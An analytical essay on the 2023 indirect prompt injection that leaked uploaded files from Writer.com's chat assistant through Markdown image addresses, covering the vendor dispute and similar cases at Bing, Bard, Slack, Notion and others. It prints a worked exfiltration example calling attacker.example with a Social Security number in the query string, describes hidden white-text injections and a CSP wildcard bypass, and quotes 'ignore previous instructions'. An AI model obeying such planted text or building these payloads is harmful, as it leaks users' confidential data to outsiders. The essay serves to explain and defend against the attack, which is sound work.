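# The Writer.com data leak through hidden web page instructions, December 2023

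## Writer.com, and how a chat assistant can be given orders by a web page

In December 2023 the security firm PromptArmor and the researcher Kai Greshake published a demonstration of an attack on Writer.com, a business writing platform built on a large language model (LLM). An LLM is a program that is trained on text and writes a reply to whatever text it is given. PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Writer.com via Indirect Prompt Injection* (2023) shows instructions hidden in a web page making the platform send the contents of a user's uploaded file to an attacker's server, inside the address of an image. Writer had responded to the private report by saying this was not a security issue. Days after publication, its chat no longer rendered images or clickable links.

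### Writer in late 2023

May Habib and Waseem AlShikh started Writer in 2020 and sold it mainly to companies. In September 2023 it raised $100 million at a valuation of $500 million, according to SiliconANGLE's *Enterprise-focused generative AI startup Writer raises $100M* (2023), and two of its customers, Accenture and Vanguard, were among the investors. Habib (2023) reported hundreds of enterprise customers in *WRITER raises $100 million in Series B to deliver on generative AI*. She wrote that healthcare companies used the product to analyse medical records and write case summaries, and that firms that search documents for lawsuits built chatbots on Writer's models. In a May 2023 press release, Writer (2023) had also named Intuit, UnitedHealthcare and Northwestern Mutual as customers, all businesses with a good deal to lose from a leak.

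The relevant part of the product is Ask Writer, its general-purpose assistant. Writer's release notes date its relaunch as a chat with file uploads to 27 September 2023. A week later, Writer (2023) announced that users on the paid Team and Enterprise plans could give it documents, slides, spreadsheets and PDFs. Users could also reopen earlier sessions with the conversation and files still in place. In May 2024, Writer raised the limit on source material from 5,000 words, which was already enough for a client list or a payroll, though small for a legal archive.

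Some versions of Ask Writer could also read web pages. According to Writer's *App guide*, the older, pre-chat version on the paid plans could fetch and read pages that a user linked. So could a free version, which anyone could use without registering and which Writer planned to close after January 2024. The free version did not accept PDFs, but Writer encouraged its users to supply links because they made the output more accurate. The October announcement of the new chat mentions files but not links. PromptArmor nonetheless attached a web page as a source in the chat, alongside an uploaded file. The main factual dispute between the two sides became whether paying customers could do the same.

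Writer marketed its platform as secure. In a post on the company's blog, *Making the most of AI without compromising data privacy*, Weaver (2023) warned businesses about the data their staff were typing into ChatGPT and told them that with Writer "you don't have to worry about leaks". In the May press release, Habib claimed that no other generative AI on the market met Writer's security and privacy standards. Her September post listed standards and laws the platform complied with, including SOC 2 Type II (an audit of how a service company protects its customers' data) and HIPAA, the American law on health records. On 13 December, two days before publication, PromptArmor took a screenshot of Writer's security page, which read "Secure from day one".

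Most of these assurances concern Writer's own conduct. The company promised not to train its models on customers' data and to let customers run the models on their own machines. A vendor can keep such promises and still leak customers' data if a stranger's text can steer the assistant while a customer is using it.

### One stream of text

An LLM application combines the developer's standing instructions, the user's request, uploaded files, any fetched web pages and earlier messages into one sequence of text, called the model's context. The model extends this sequence one token (a word or piece of a word) at a time, each time picking a likely continuation of everything so far. Developers train these models to follow instructions in text, so a model may well act on a sentence in a fetched article that reads like a request.

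Older systems have had the same problem. Schneier (2024), in *LLMs' Data-Control Path Insecurity*, compares it to the telephone network when callers could whistle commands to the switching equipment, because commands and voices travelled down the same line. A redesign moved the commands to a separate channel, so whistling no longer had any effect.

In an SQL injection attack, someone types a database command into a web form that expects, say, a surname, and the database runs it. Programmers prevent this with parameterised queries, which pass the surname separately from the command so that the database never runs it. An LLM has no such separation. David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, bases his argument in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* on this difference. He writes that inside the model there is no data or instruction, "only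 ever 'next token'". His example is a recruiter's tool that scores CVs. A candidate hides a line of text in a CV telling the model to ignore its previous instructions and approve the CV for interview, and the model may do it.

Models often ignore instructions planted in a web page. Developers can make attacks less likely to succeed by training a model to give priority to its proper instructions, or by putting markers around untrusted text. But the markers are tokens like any others, and an attacker can keep rewording the attack. In December 2025, David C wrote that it was quite possible nobody would ever fix the problem the way parameterised queries fixed SQL injection. These measures are worth using in a system that holds confidential files, but they don't replace a security boundary.

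### Prompt injection, direct and indirect

Prompt injection is text that makes a model follow an attacker's instructions instead of its user's or developer's. In *Trust No AI* (2024), the security researcher Johann Rehberger credits the discovery to the company Preamble, which reported it privately to OpenAI in May 2022, and the name to the programmer Simon Willison. In the early cases, the attacker was the chatbot's own user, trying to get it to break its rules or reveal its developer's instructions.

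Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023) introduced indirect prompt injection in *Not what you've signed up for*, first posted in February 2023 and later revised. In this attack, the user is innocent, and the attacker places text in material that the model reads for the user, such as a web page or an email. Companies were just starting to connect models to search engines, inboxes and document stores, all of which bring in text written by strangers. Greshake and colleagues argue that when a model connected in this way processes a retrieved page, it is like running a program from an unknown source. The attacker doesn't need access to the application, only a page that the application is likely to read.

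To test this, the researchers built mock assistants on OpenAI's models and gave them tools for searching the web, opening URLs, handling email and storing notes. The tools returned prepared content, so nothing touched a real system. In one trial, an email containing hidden instructions made the assistant send the same instructions to the user's contacts. In another, the assistant saved part of the attack in its notes, and when it read them in a new session, it came under the attacker's control again.

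They also attacked a real product, Microsoft's Bing Chat, which could read whatever page the user had open in the browser. They put orders in an HTML comment, a part of a page's code that visitors do not see, telling the model to get the user's real name without raising suspicion. One of the researchers, playing the user, asked about tomorrow's weather. Bing Chat answered, asked about plans for the day, learned that the user was a journalist and asked whether they wrote under a pen name. Once it had a name, it offered a link to a "secret online community" whose address ended with the name in scrambled form. Bing Chat's filters ended the session when a user typed a known jailbreak (wording that gets a model to ignore its restrictions), but let similar wording through when it arrived in a page.

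The paper gives no success rates, and the team tested Bing Chat on files on their own computers to avoid planting live attacks on the web. Their injections into the code assistant GitHub Copilot were much less effective inside larger programs. But many of the prompts worked as first written, and the team left the spelling mistakes in to show this. The results are good evidence that the attack was possible and took little effort, but weak evidence about how often it would succeed against a given product.

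One obstacle remained for the thief in the Bing Chat trial: the user had to click the link.

### The image, the request and the policy

A model's reply is only text, and generating it sends nothing to a third party. The reply can leak data only if another component acts on it. In a chat product, that component can be the user's own browser, and an attacker can use ordinary web features to make it send the data.

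Chat windows commonly format replies with Markdown, a set of short text codes for headings, bold type, links and pictures. The code for an image is `![caption](address)`. When a reply contains this code, the chat window replaces it with the picture at that address. The address can be anywhere on the web, and the model can write the code as easily as any other text.

To show the picture, the browser must first fetch it. It sends a GET request, the standard request for a file, to the server named in the address, and it does so as soon as the reply appears, without asking anyone. The request contains the full address, and an address can have query parameters attached to its end: named pieces of data, after a question mark, which the server can read and record. One of the addresses in Samoilenko, in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, ends like this:

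`pixel.png?p=What%20is%20the%20tallest%20building%20in%20the%20world%3F`

The parameter `p` contains a question that the user had asked ChatGPT, with `%20` standing for a space. Whoever runs the server can read the question in the log. This is data exfiltration, the moving of private data out of a system to someone who should not have it. The picture itself hardly matters, and Samoilenko used a single transparent pixel.

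A website can restrict these requests with a Content Security Policy (CSP), a list of the domains from which the browser may load images and other content. If an image's domain is not on the list, the browser does not send the request or the data in it. But a CSP checks only where a request is going, not what data the address contains, so an attacker can still get data out if the list includes even one domain on which outsiders can set up their own server. Writer had a CSP in December 2023, and PromptArmor found such a domain on it.

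### The image channel before Writer

All of this was public by the time PromptArmor approached Writer. Roman Samoilenko, a software engineer, found at the end of March 2023 that ChatGPT could leak data through an image's address. In his attack, the victim copies text from the attacker's website, and a script on the site secretly adds instructions to the clipboard. When the victim pastes the text into ChatGPT, the instructions tell the model to end its answer with an invisible image and to put material from the conversation into the image's address. Another line tells the model to do the same in every later answer, so the attacker keeps receiving whatever the victim types.

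Samoilenko acknowledged that the model's output varied between runs, so the same prompt might work once and then fail. He also acknowledged that while earlier prompts and code were easy to extract, passwords and API keys (the credentials that programs use to log in to services) were very difficult. He still thought that OpenAI should stop ChatGPT from replying with images. On 14 April, Willison (2023) shared the finding on his widely followed blog under the same title.

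Rehberger independently found the channel in early April, a few days after Samoilenko, and removed the need for copying and pasting. In *ChatGPT Plugins*, he used add-ons that let ChatGPT open web pages or read video transcripts, so the attacker's text reached the model through the page itself. The text contained instructions to summarise the conversation so far and attach the summary to an image address. When the browser loaded the image, it sent the summary to the attacker. This attack combined indirect prompt injection with the image channel. PromptArmor later used the same combination against Writer, but took an uploaded file instead of chat history.

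Rehberger practised responsible disclosure, reporting flaws privately to the vendor and allowing time for a fix before publishing them. He reported the flaw in Bing Chat to Microsoft on 8 April, and Microsoft fixed it on 15 June, according to *Bing Chat*, a post on his blog, Embrace The Red. He contacted OpenAI on 9 April, and the company replied that displaying images was a feature. He later listed eleven products in which he had found and reported the same flaw, including Anthropic's Claude, Google's Bard and Discord, though he made some of those reports after the Writer leak.

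The Bard case, the work of Rehberger, Joseph Thacker and Kai Greshake, became public at the start of November 2023. Google had recently given Bard, its chatbot, access to users' personal documents, and the attack arrived in a Google Doc shared with the victim. Google's CSP allowed images only from Google's own domains. *Hacking Google Bard* (Willison, 2023) explained that this did not stop the attack, because Google lets anyone run small programs on one of those domains, and such a program can collect the data. Google fixed the flaw promptly. Willison called such attacks inevitable wherever a system combines private data with untrusted input. He later added a third ingredient, a way to send data out, and named the combination the lethal trifecta. On 29 November 2023, PromptArmor sent its report to Writer.

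## What PromptArmor demonstrated, and its case that this was a vulnerability

### From the request to the attacker's log

PromptArmor and Greshake played both the customer and the attacker. As the customer, they opened a chat in Ask Writer and asked for a report. They added a web article called "Intro to SaaS" (software as a service, which companies rent by subscription) as a source and uploaded a text file, `client_data.txt`. The file contained customers' names and Social Security numbers, revenue figures and executives' salaries, all invented.

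PromptArmor, acting as the attacker, had prepared the article. It looked like an ordinary introduction to the subject but contained a passage in small white type on a white background, which a reader would probably notice only by selecting the text with the mouse. An application that fetches a page for a model typically keeps the words and drops the styling, so the model receives the hidden passage as ordinary text. The trick is also common. *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari, Acharya and colleagues, 2026) found 15,387 instructions aimed at AI systems in web pages and server responses, and in 2,397 cases the text was nearly the same colour as its background.

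*Data exfiltration from Writer.com with indirect prompt injection* (Willison, 2023) quotes part of the hidden passage. It told the model to end its summary with a Markdown image from a certain address, and to attach a query parameter named `document_content` containing text from the uploaded files. It called them the files "I uploaded", as if the user were speaking. The quoted part adds a step to the task the model is already doing and doesn't tell it to ignore its earlier instructions.

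The model wrote the summary and then the code for an image, copying the client data from its context into the image's address. When the chat window displayed the image, the browser requested it from the researchers' server. Willison describes the image as invisible. Even a visible one might have passed for part of the report, because its file name was `saas_trends_4.png`.

PromptArmor published screenshots of the request in the browser's network panel, the same data in the server's log, and the original file next to the request. These are the best evidence in the post because the log shows that the data arrived. A screenshot of the chat alone would have shown only that the model wrote a strange address.

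### A small example

Suppose a bookkeeper uploads a file with a single line in it:

`Ana Ruiz, SSN 000-12-3456, salary 84000`

The bookkeeper also adds a web page whose hidden text asks for an image from `attacker.example`. At the end of its summary, the model writes:

`![Trends](https://attacker.example/trends.png?document_content=Ana%20Ruiz%2C%20SSN%20000-12-3456%2C%20salary%2084000)`

The bookkeeper sees only the picture. To fetch it, the browser sends the attacker's server a request that begins:

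```
GET /trends.png?document_content=Ana%20Ruiz%2C%20SSN%20000-12-3456%2C%20salary%2084000
Host: attacker.example
```

The attacker can read the record in the server's log almost as it appears in the file, with the code `%2C` standing for a comma. PromptArmor used the logs of CloudFront, a service from Amazon Web Services (AWS) that stores copies of customers' files around the world so that web pages load quickly. According to AWS's *Standard logging reference*, each entry includes the query string (everything after the question mark), the time and the visitor's IP address. The logs usually arrive within an hour. They include failed requests, so the picture doesn't have to exist.

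One image can carry only a limited amount of data this way. CloudFront cannot log a request whose address is longer than 8,192 bytes, which leaves room for roughly a thousand words of English once each space takes up three characters. A short client list fits easily, but an attacker would have to spread a 5,000-word file, the longest Writer accepted at the time, over several images. Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026), in *Silent Egress*, split stolen data across several requests, though their test agent sent the requests itself and did not rely on images. PromptArmor does not report trying this on Writer.

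### Why the Content Security Policy did not stop it

Writer's Content Security Policy would have blocked the bookkeeper's image because `attacker.example` was not on the list. But the list included `*.cloudfront.net`. CentralCSP's *Host source* explains that a wildcard (`*`) in this position allows any subdomain, meaning any name in front of `.cloudfront.net`.

Anyone with an AWS account can get such a name. According to AWS's *Create a distribution*, the customer specifies where the files are, and CloudFront assigns an address such as `d111111abcdef8.cloudfront.net`. PromptArmor got an address of this kind and put it in the hidden instruction. The browser checked the address against the list in Writer's policy, found a match, and sent the request with the client data attached, as the policy allowed.

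An attacker could have read all of this in a browser's developer tools, because a website sends its policy to the browser of everyone who visits.

Writer probably listed the domain because it kept some of its own images on CloudFront, although neither PromptArmor nor Willison gives the reason. If so, it could more safely have listed only the exact addresses that CloudFront had assigned to it, and the browser would then have refused to load images from any other CloudFront customer. AWS never gives an old address to a new customer, so these entries would have stayed safe even after Writer stopped using the addresses. CentralCSP's *img-src*, a guide to the part of the policy that covers images, warns against allowing images from every host because any host could then receive data. Writer's list was much narrower, but it gave little protection against an attacker willing to open an AWS account.

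### The same data in a link

PromptArmor also sent Writer videos of two attacks that used a link instead of an image. In one, the hidden text contained an instruction to add a "learn more" link to the model's answer, with the contents of the uploaded files in the link's address. In the other, the address contained the first three messages of the conversation. The second attack could harm a user who had uploaded nothing, because the messages themselves may be sensitive, as in a chat about planned layoffs.

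A link sends nothing until the user clicks it, and the user may ignore it or hover over it and notice that the address is suspiciously long. The image was clearly the more dangerous of the two on Writer because it needed no click, so it worked on every user whose chat displayed the answer, including careful ones. PromptArmor calls the image method "zero-click" in a later report, *HuggingFace Chat Exfiltrates Data*.

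The link does have one advantage for the attacker, which is that it can lead to any domain. The policy's list of image sources doesn't apply to pages the user opens by clicking. If Writer had removed only CloudFront's wildcard from the list, it would have blocked this image, but both link attacks would still have worked.

Requiring a click also does little to protect users. People expect to see "learn more" under a summary of a web article, and the attacker can make the link open a real article, so even a user who clicks notices nothing wrong. In July 2026, The Hacker News' *Writer AI Flaw Could Let Agent Previews Leak Session Tokens Across Tenants* (2026) described another Writer flaw, since patched, as critical even though it needed a click. That flaw was more serious than this one, because the click could give an outsider the victim's whole account rather than one file.

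Messaging apps often fetch a link themselves to show a preview of the page. TechNadu's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* reports on later PromptArmor research in which the preview alone delivered the data to the attacker. In Writer's own chat, though, the attack still depended on the user.

### The researchers' case

PromptArmor's case rests mainly on how ordinary the user's behaviour was. The user asked for a report, added a source and uploaded a file, which is what the product was for. They didn't install anything, type a password into a strange site or, in the image attack, click on anything. The usual security advice to office workers wouldn't have helped, because the instructions were in white text that users were unlikely to notice unless they selected it.

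The user also got no warning. Writer's chat displayed the answer without asking whether to contact an outside server, and the answer contained the summary the user wanted. Someone who later suspected a leak would have had to check the image addresses in the browser's network panel.

The attacker needed only a web page and an AWS account, without access to Writer's systems or the customer's account. PromptArmor adds that the attacker doesn't have to own the page, since they can also hide instructions on other sites, such as social media platforms.

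Willison notes that Writer also marketed itself as a "secure enterprise generative AI platform". A customer who uploads salaries to such a service agrees to let the service process them, but not to let whoever wrote a web article read them. On most understandings of the word, a product has a vulnerability if an outsider can use it to take data that its owner meant to keep private, and PromptArmor had done this with Writer's product as it stood. Writer rejected the report on the ground that real customers' accounts could not reach websites, which disputes who was exposed but not how the attack worked.

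PromptArmor makes a strong case that the flaw existed, but its evidence on how likely the flaw was to hurt anyone is weaker. For data to be stolen, a user has to add the attacker's page to a chat that also contains something worth stealing, and the model has to follow the page's hidden text. PromptArmor supplied both the page and the file, so it tested only whether the model would follow the text and whether the technical steps after that would work.

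### The limits of the evidence

PromptArmor does not say how many attempts it made or how many of them worked. One success is little evidence of how often an attack works, and success rates in later studies varied widely. Lan and colleagues built an agent on a small open model, put a secret in its context and asked it to summarise pages containing hidden instructions. The agent sent the secret out in about 89% of 480 runs. Khodayari and colleagues ran 5,200 trials on 13 models, using instructions they had found on the live web. The models followed the instructions at most 8% of the time, a rate reached by smaller models reading plain text. When the input kept the page's structure, the rate fell to between 0.2% and 1.1%.

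Part of the gap must come from differences in the instructions. Lan and colleagues wrote theirs for the agent they were attacking, whereas many of those on the web are crude, such as orders to ignore everything and return random numbers. PromptArmor's was also written for its target and fitted the user's request, so it may well have worked more often than the crude ones, but neither study gives a figure for Writer's chat in 2023. Even a low success rate could be enough for an attacker. At 8%, a page that reached a hundred users with confidential files in their chats would leak files from about eight of them.

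Neither PromptArmor's post nor Willison's reports a theft from a real customer. This is only mildly reassuring, because a successful theft would have looked to the victim like an ordinary picture loading, and the clearest record of it would have been in the attacker's own log. Khodayari and colleagues provide better evidence that such attacks are rare. They searched 1.2 billion web addresses, mostly from an October 2025 crawl, and found 15,387 instructions there and in two smaller sources. Only 13 were attempts to extract data, of which nine were aimed at the developer's standing instructions and four at other secrets. However, the search relied on a list of known phrases, such as "ignore previous instructions". A search of this kind might have missed the passage that Willison quotes, which contains nothing so obvious.

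PromptArmor says that it extracted all of the sensitive information in its file, and its screenshots compare the whole file with the request. But the instruction, as Willison quotes it, specifies only the middle 50 characters of the uploaded files. Neither source explains the difference. The researchers may have used several versions of the instruction, or the model may have exceeded the limit, since models read text in tokens and are bad at counting characters. The difference hardly affects whether Writer had a flaw, because 50 characters are enough for a name and a Social Security number, and an attacker can ask for more. It matters more for judging the flaw's severity, because it is unclear how reliably the model could copy out a long file.

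PromptArmor had something to gain from the publicity. Y Combinator's *PromptArmor*, an entry in the start-up investor's directory, lists the company as founded in 2023 and its business as "LLM Security and Compliance." The company now sells daily monitoring of the AI features in products its customers buy from other vendors, and finding a flaw in a platform with famous clients is good advertising for that service. This may have influenced which product PromptArmor tested and how strongly it worded the result. It writes that the injection overrides "any security filters" Writer had enforced, but the test shows only that whatever filters were in place failed to stop this one injection. The records of the request are harder to dismiss as marketing. Writer had received the screenshots and videos more than two weeks before publication and could have repeated the test itself.

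## Why Writer rejected the report, and whether its reason held

Writer rejected the report after six days and gave its reason in one sentence. The only account of the exchange is a timeline at the end of PromptArmor's post.

| Date in 2023 | What happened |
|---|---|
| 29 November | PromptArmor sends the report, with videos, to Writer's chief technology officer and security team. Writer asks for more details, and PromptArmor replies with a fuller description and screenshots. |
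| 1 December | PromptArmor writes again. |
| 4 December | PromptArmor sends a new version of the video with a spoken explanation and asks about Writer's disclosure policy. |
| 5 December | Writer rejects the report. PromptArmor answers that paid accounts have the same flaw and that it is writing a post to warn users. Writer does not reply. |
| 15 December | PromptArmor publishes the post on Hacker News, a discussion site popular with programmers. |

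On 5 December, Writer replied that it did not consider this a security issue because "real customer accounts do not have access to any website". It does not seem to have commented publicly, then or since. A week after the researchers published their report, Schneier (2023) described the attack on his security blog in *Data Exfiltration Using Indirect Prompt Injection*, quoting only the researchers. PromptArmor may have left out other things Writer wrote, but it is unlikely to have misquoted this sentence, since Writer had the original message and could have published it.

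PromptArmor published sixteen days after reporting the flaw, which is a short wait. In Embrace The Red's *Bobby Tables but with LLM Apps* (2024), Rehberger gives three to four months as the industry norm for unfixed flaws. He had reported a similar leak in NotebookLM, Google's tool for asking questions about one's own documents, on 4 December 2023, the day before Writer's refusal. He waited 132 days before publishing. But Google had confirmed that flaw and might have been working on a fix. Writer had told PromptArmor that there was nothing to fix, so a longer wait would mainly have kept customers from learning about the flaw. Publishing early did mean that for a few days anyone could read how to carry out an attack that still worked.

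### Could a paying customer's chat read a web page?

If Writer was right about its accounts, it had a fair reason to reject the attack as PromptArmor had demonstrated it. The hidden instructions were on a web page. If a chat cannot fetch web pages, those instructions never enter the model's context, so they cannot make the model write the image.

Customers were still not necessarily safe, because they could upload files, which can also come from strangers. PromptArmor's *Notion AI* describes an attack on the workspace app Notion that hid instructions in a job applicant's CV, in white one-point type with a white image on top. A recruiter might have uploaded the same CV to Writer alongside a table of salaries. Nobody seems to have tried this on Writer, but the chat window would presumably still have displayed the image produced by the instructions.

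The word "real" in Writer's answer is a little odd. It suggests the company thought the researchers had used a free or trial account, with web access that paying customers lacked. People with free accounts can lose data too, though Writer could reasonably have treated that as less urgent than a leak from a hospital's account.

PromptArmor replied the same day that paid accounts had the same flaw, but it does not explain how it knew. It does not state which type of account its screenshots show, and it describes no test on a paid one. According to Writer's guide to the app, the older version of Ask Writer on the paid plans could read pages that a user linked. In its announcement of the newer chat, Writer mentioned only files. Writer's claim about "any website" therefore looks too broad, but the guide doesn't prove that a paying customer could have reproduced PromptArmor's attack in the new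 chat.

Either side could probably have settled this in an afternoon by testing an ordinary account on the Team plan and another on the Enterprise plan. With each account, the tester asks the chat to summarise a new page on a server that the tester controls. The page contains a made-up word that appears nowhere else. If the word turns up in the summary, the account can read websites, and the server's log should show the request for the page. The tester then adds the hidden instruction to the page, uploads a file of invented data and looks for that data in the log. The tester should record the two results separately, because the model may ignore the instruction on one attempt even if the account can read the page. A screenshot showing the plan's name would have let outsiders check the answer.

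Writer was in the better position to run this test because it knew which features it had switched on for each plan and could create as many test accounts as it liked. PromptArmor's reply also gave it a specific reason to doubt what it had just written. If the timeline is complete, Writer's silence after that reply is harder to defend than the rejection. A security team can easily be wrong about one feature of a newly relaunched product, but it ought to look again when someone with a working demonstration contradicts it.

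Writer's later decision to stop displaying images does not show who was right about the accounts. The company may have discovered that paying customers were at risk, wanted to protect free users, or wanted to end the bad publicity.

### Did Writer misunderstand the flaw?

Willison calls Writer's answer "a huge failure" and sees it as an example of how people struggle to understand prompt injection, however clearly someone explains it. In an interview with the analyst firm RedMonk that month, he suggested that one cause is that people confuse prompt injection with moderation, or stopping a model from saying offensive or dangerous things.

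Willison said that a user who tricks a chatbot into giving a recipe for napalm embarrasses its developer but does limited damage, because the user could have found the recipe elsewhere. An attacker who injects instructions into a system with private data can take that data. He therefore thinks a defence that works 99% of the time is inadequate, since attackers will keep trying until they find the 1% that gets through. He also pointed to Purple Llama, a set of safety tools that Meta had just released, whose 27-page paper mentioned prompt injection once and defined it as an attempt to get round content restrictions, as in the napalm example.

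Writer's sentence doesn't show this confusion. Whoever wrote it apparently understood that the attack came through a web page, but denied that customers could load one. If that denial was wrong, the mistake was about Writer's own product. They may also have missed that a file could carry the same instructions, which would be closer to what Willison means, but one sentence isn't enough to tell.

His explanation fits Slack, the workplace messaging service, much better. In August 2024, PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection* described an attack on Slack's AI assistant. A user keeps an API key in a private channel, and an attacker with an account in the same workspace posts an instruction in a public channel. When the user asks the assistant for the key, it retrieves both messages and follows the attacker's instruction. It shows a false error message with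 a link to "reauthenticate". The link's address contains the key, so clicking it sends the key to the attacker.

Five days after receiving the report, Slack replied that the evidence was insufficient and that letting any member of a workspace search its public channels was "intended behavior". That was true, but the key was in the private channel, and only the attacker's instruction was public. Slack defended the rule that let the assistant read the instruction but overlooked what the assistant did next. PromptArmor still credits Slack's team with replying promptly and making a real attempt to understand the problem.

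After publication, Slack investigated and issued a patch. In a statement reproduced in Digital Trends' *Slack patches potential AI security issue*, it stressed that the attack worked only "under very limited and specific circumstances" and that the attacker needed an account in the same workspace. It said it had no evidence of unauthorised access to customers' data. Needing an account makes an attack less likely, although PromptArmor thought a poisoned PDF might let an attacker do without one. Writer could not have made the same defence, because an attacker can put instructions on a web page without having a Writer account.

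### The reasons other vendors gave

Writer claimed only that customers faced no risk, and never argued that they should bear the risk themselves. Other vendors that rejected similar reports did argue about responsibility, and Writer could have made the same arguments if its claim about accounts had failed.

OpenAI gave the simplest reason, that displaying images was a feature. According to *ChatGPT Plugins*, it planned no changes even after Rehberger had pointed out that plugins would let an attacker exploit the images remotely. But nearly every leak of this kind uses a feature. A vendor also has to explain why a stranger should be able to choose the image's address and have the model put the user's data in it, and on Rehberger's account OpenAI didn't. PromptArmor mentioned OpenAI's refusal in its post about Writer, so in early December Writer could have cited the best-known company in the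 field in its support. It would have lost that support by 21 December, when Willison, in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, reported that OpenAI had begun to check images before displaying them.

Microsoft gave a much fuller answer two years later. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* describes an attack in which instructions in an online resource, such as an article, make Microsoft's Copilot Chat load an image and leak an API key from a developer's working environment. Checkmarx, a software security company, reported this on 15 October 2025. Microsoft replied on 4 November that it did not classify the behaviour as a vulnerability. It said that the attack needed several actions that users do not take by default, that it did not work reliably in different environments, and that the product displayed warnings. Microsoft also assumed that people at work review and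 trust the code they choose to run. It still passed the report to its engineers so they could consider making the behaviour more visible to users.

These are sensible questions to ask about a reported flaw, but the answers to most of them would have counted against Writer. The user in PromptArmor's report had done nothing unusual and had seen no warning. A marketing employee who asks for a summary of an article also isn't choosing to run code in any normal sense. Only the objection about reliability might have helped Writer, since PromptArmor never published a success rate, but Writer didn't raise that objection.

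Checkmarx also reported to Google that its Gemini assistant could leak data through clickable links. Gemini already blocked external images, so the attack required the victim to click. Google closed the report after four days, saying the problem was infeasible to fix and not severe enough to track as a security bug. Checkmarx finds this acceptable but argues that Google should warn users, since it has left them to manage the risk. Leaving the risk to users who have been warned seems fair for links, which they can choose not to open, but Writer's users could not choose whether the image loaded.

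Google took a different position on Antigravity, its AI code editor, in November 2025. PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* describes how instructions in a web page could make the editor steal a programmer's credentials, and it characterises Google's approach as a disclaimer about existing risks. Willison notes that Google publicly listed such leaks as "known issues" that it was working to fix. Under reward rules that Google (2023) published for its AI products, researchers earn nothing for an issue the company already knows about, but by giving this answer Google concedes that the flaw exists. Willison also quotes another researcher who had reported a leak through images in Antigravity and said that Google marked it as intended behaviour, which is much harder to reconcile with a promised fix.

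A known issue can still harm users until it is fixed. According to Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE*, Google built its Antigravity editor on code licensed from Windsurf, to which Rehberger had reported flaws in May 2025. He found the same flaws in Google's version, and Google began to list them publicly only after researchers had started sending reports. In June 2026, *Faking the Pipeline* (Odson and Morris, 2026) demonstrated another leak from Antigravity, this time through its ability to display images in the chat.

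In 2025, the makers of Cursor, a code editor, also called a similar leak a known issue. They advised users to review the outside services they connected and to use only those with trusted content. Willison objects that this is difficult in practice because attackers have so many ways to get instructions into material that looks safe. For Writer, the equivalent advice would have been to add only trustworthy web pages, but a customer who followed it carefully could still have missed instructions hidden in white text.

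Google fixed a similar flaw in Bard in 2023, which makes all these refusals look less inevitable. Rehberger reported that attack on 19 September. When he asked for an update a month later because he wanted to show the attack at a conference, Google told him it had already fixed the flaw. Greshake had also worked on the attack, so he had recently seen a vendor accept a report much like the one he and PromptArmor sent to Writer.

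There is a strong case that Writer was responsible, even if some doubt remains about who was at risk. Writer decided whether its chat displayed images and which domains its policy allowed. Customers could not edit the policy, and PromptArmor mentions no setting that would have let them turn images off. They could avoid sources that looked suspicious, but if they trusted a malicious one, only Writer could stop the browser from sending their files to it.

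### Reports that nobody at the vendor had read

Many companies pay an outside service to handle triage, the first judgement on whether a report describes a real security flaw and how urgent it is. A rejection may therefore reflect the service's opinion rather than the vendor's, and if the service wrongly rejects a report, the vendor may never see it.

PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* describes a flaw in the page where developers read records of their applications' conversations. An application might block an answer that contained a malicious image, but when a developer opened the blocked answer in OpenAI's log viewer to see what had gone wrong, the viewer displayed the image and the developer's browser sent the user's data to the attacker. PromptArmor reported the flaw through the reporting service Bugcrowd on 17 November 2025 and answered questions on three days the following week. Bugcrowd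 closed the report as "not applicable" during triage on 4 December. OpenAI first learned of the flaw from PromptArmor's article. It then confirmed the problem, reopened the report on 22 January 2026 and started on a fix.

The Notion case followed the same pattern, but faster. Notion's assistant saved an edit containing an external image before asking the user to approve it, so the browser requested the image before the user could answer. PromptArmor reported this on 24 December 2025 through HackerOne, another reporting service, whose triage team closed the report as not applicable five days later. PromptArmor published its findings on 7 January 2026. Notion's own staff contacted PromptArmor the same day and had a fix in place by that night.

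HackerOne must have known about this kind of attack. One of its directors, Singh, uses the Bard leak as a real-world example of prompt injection in *How a Prompt Injection Vulnerability Led to Data Exfiltration*. In the OpenAI case, PromptArmor's explanation is that such reports are hard to triage because they often fit none of the established categories of flaw. A triager in that case also had to follow the data through two products, the application that blocked the image and the viewer that displayed it.

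A vendor's own process for handling reports can fail in much the same way. In August 2024, Rehberger reported a leak through images in Google AI Studio, a site for trying out Google's models, but he got no date for a fix through the official channel. According to Embrace The Red's *Google AI Studio*, he then tagged Logan Kilpatrick of Google in a public post, and the company fixed the flaw within 24 hours. Google was evidently willing to fix it once the report reached someone who would act on it.

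On 1 December 2025, PromptArmor told Hugging Face, which runs a platform for sharing AI models, that its chat application, HuggingChat, had a flaw almost identical to Writer's. A web page could make the model put financial figures from an uploaded file into the address of a one-pixel image. Hugging Face did not reply, and PromptArmor eventually published its findings. Hugging Face may have disagreed, missed the message or been busy, so it would be unfair to count its silence as a rejection.

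Writer's rejection was different because it began as a disagreement about a fact. PromptArmor had written directly to Writer's technology chief and security team, and Writer replied within a day, asked for details and gave its own reason for rejecting the report. On 5 December, PromptArmor disputed Writer's factual claim, and Writer stopped answering.

### Writer's rules for reporting flaws

PromptArmor asked about Writer's disclosure policy on 4 December, and its timeline records no answer. Writer now has a policy in a version from January 2024, the month after the leak became public. The date alone doesn't show that the leak prompted this version, and Writer may well have had an earlier one.

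Writer's *Vulnerability disclosure program* (2024) commits the company to making a reasonable effort to respond to new reports within three business days. It sets no target for triage or a fix, since both depend on how severe and complex the flaw is. Writer would have met this standard in 2023, because it first replied to PromptArmor on the day the report arrived. The delay that mattered came after PromptArmor disputed the rejection, and the policy has no procedure for a researcher who thinks Writer has made a mistake.

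Writer has a long list of issues it will not accept, but prompt injection is not on it. The list does exclude "missing best practices" in a Content Security Policy, so Writer would probably reject a report that only showed its policy allowed every CloudFront address. A researcher who used such an address to extract a file would have a much stronger case. Writer also excludes flaws that need "unlikely user interaction". It might try to apply this to the links in PromptArmor's videos, but it could hardly apply it to the image, because the user only had to ask for a summary.

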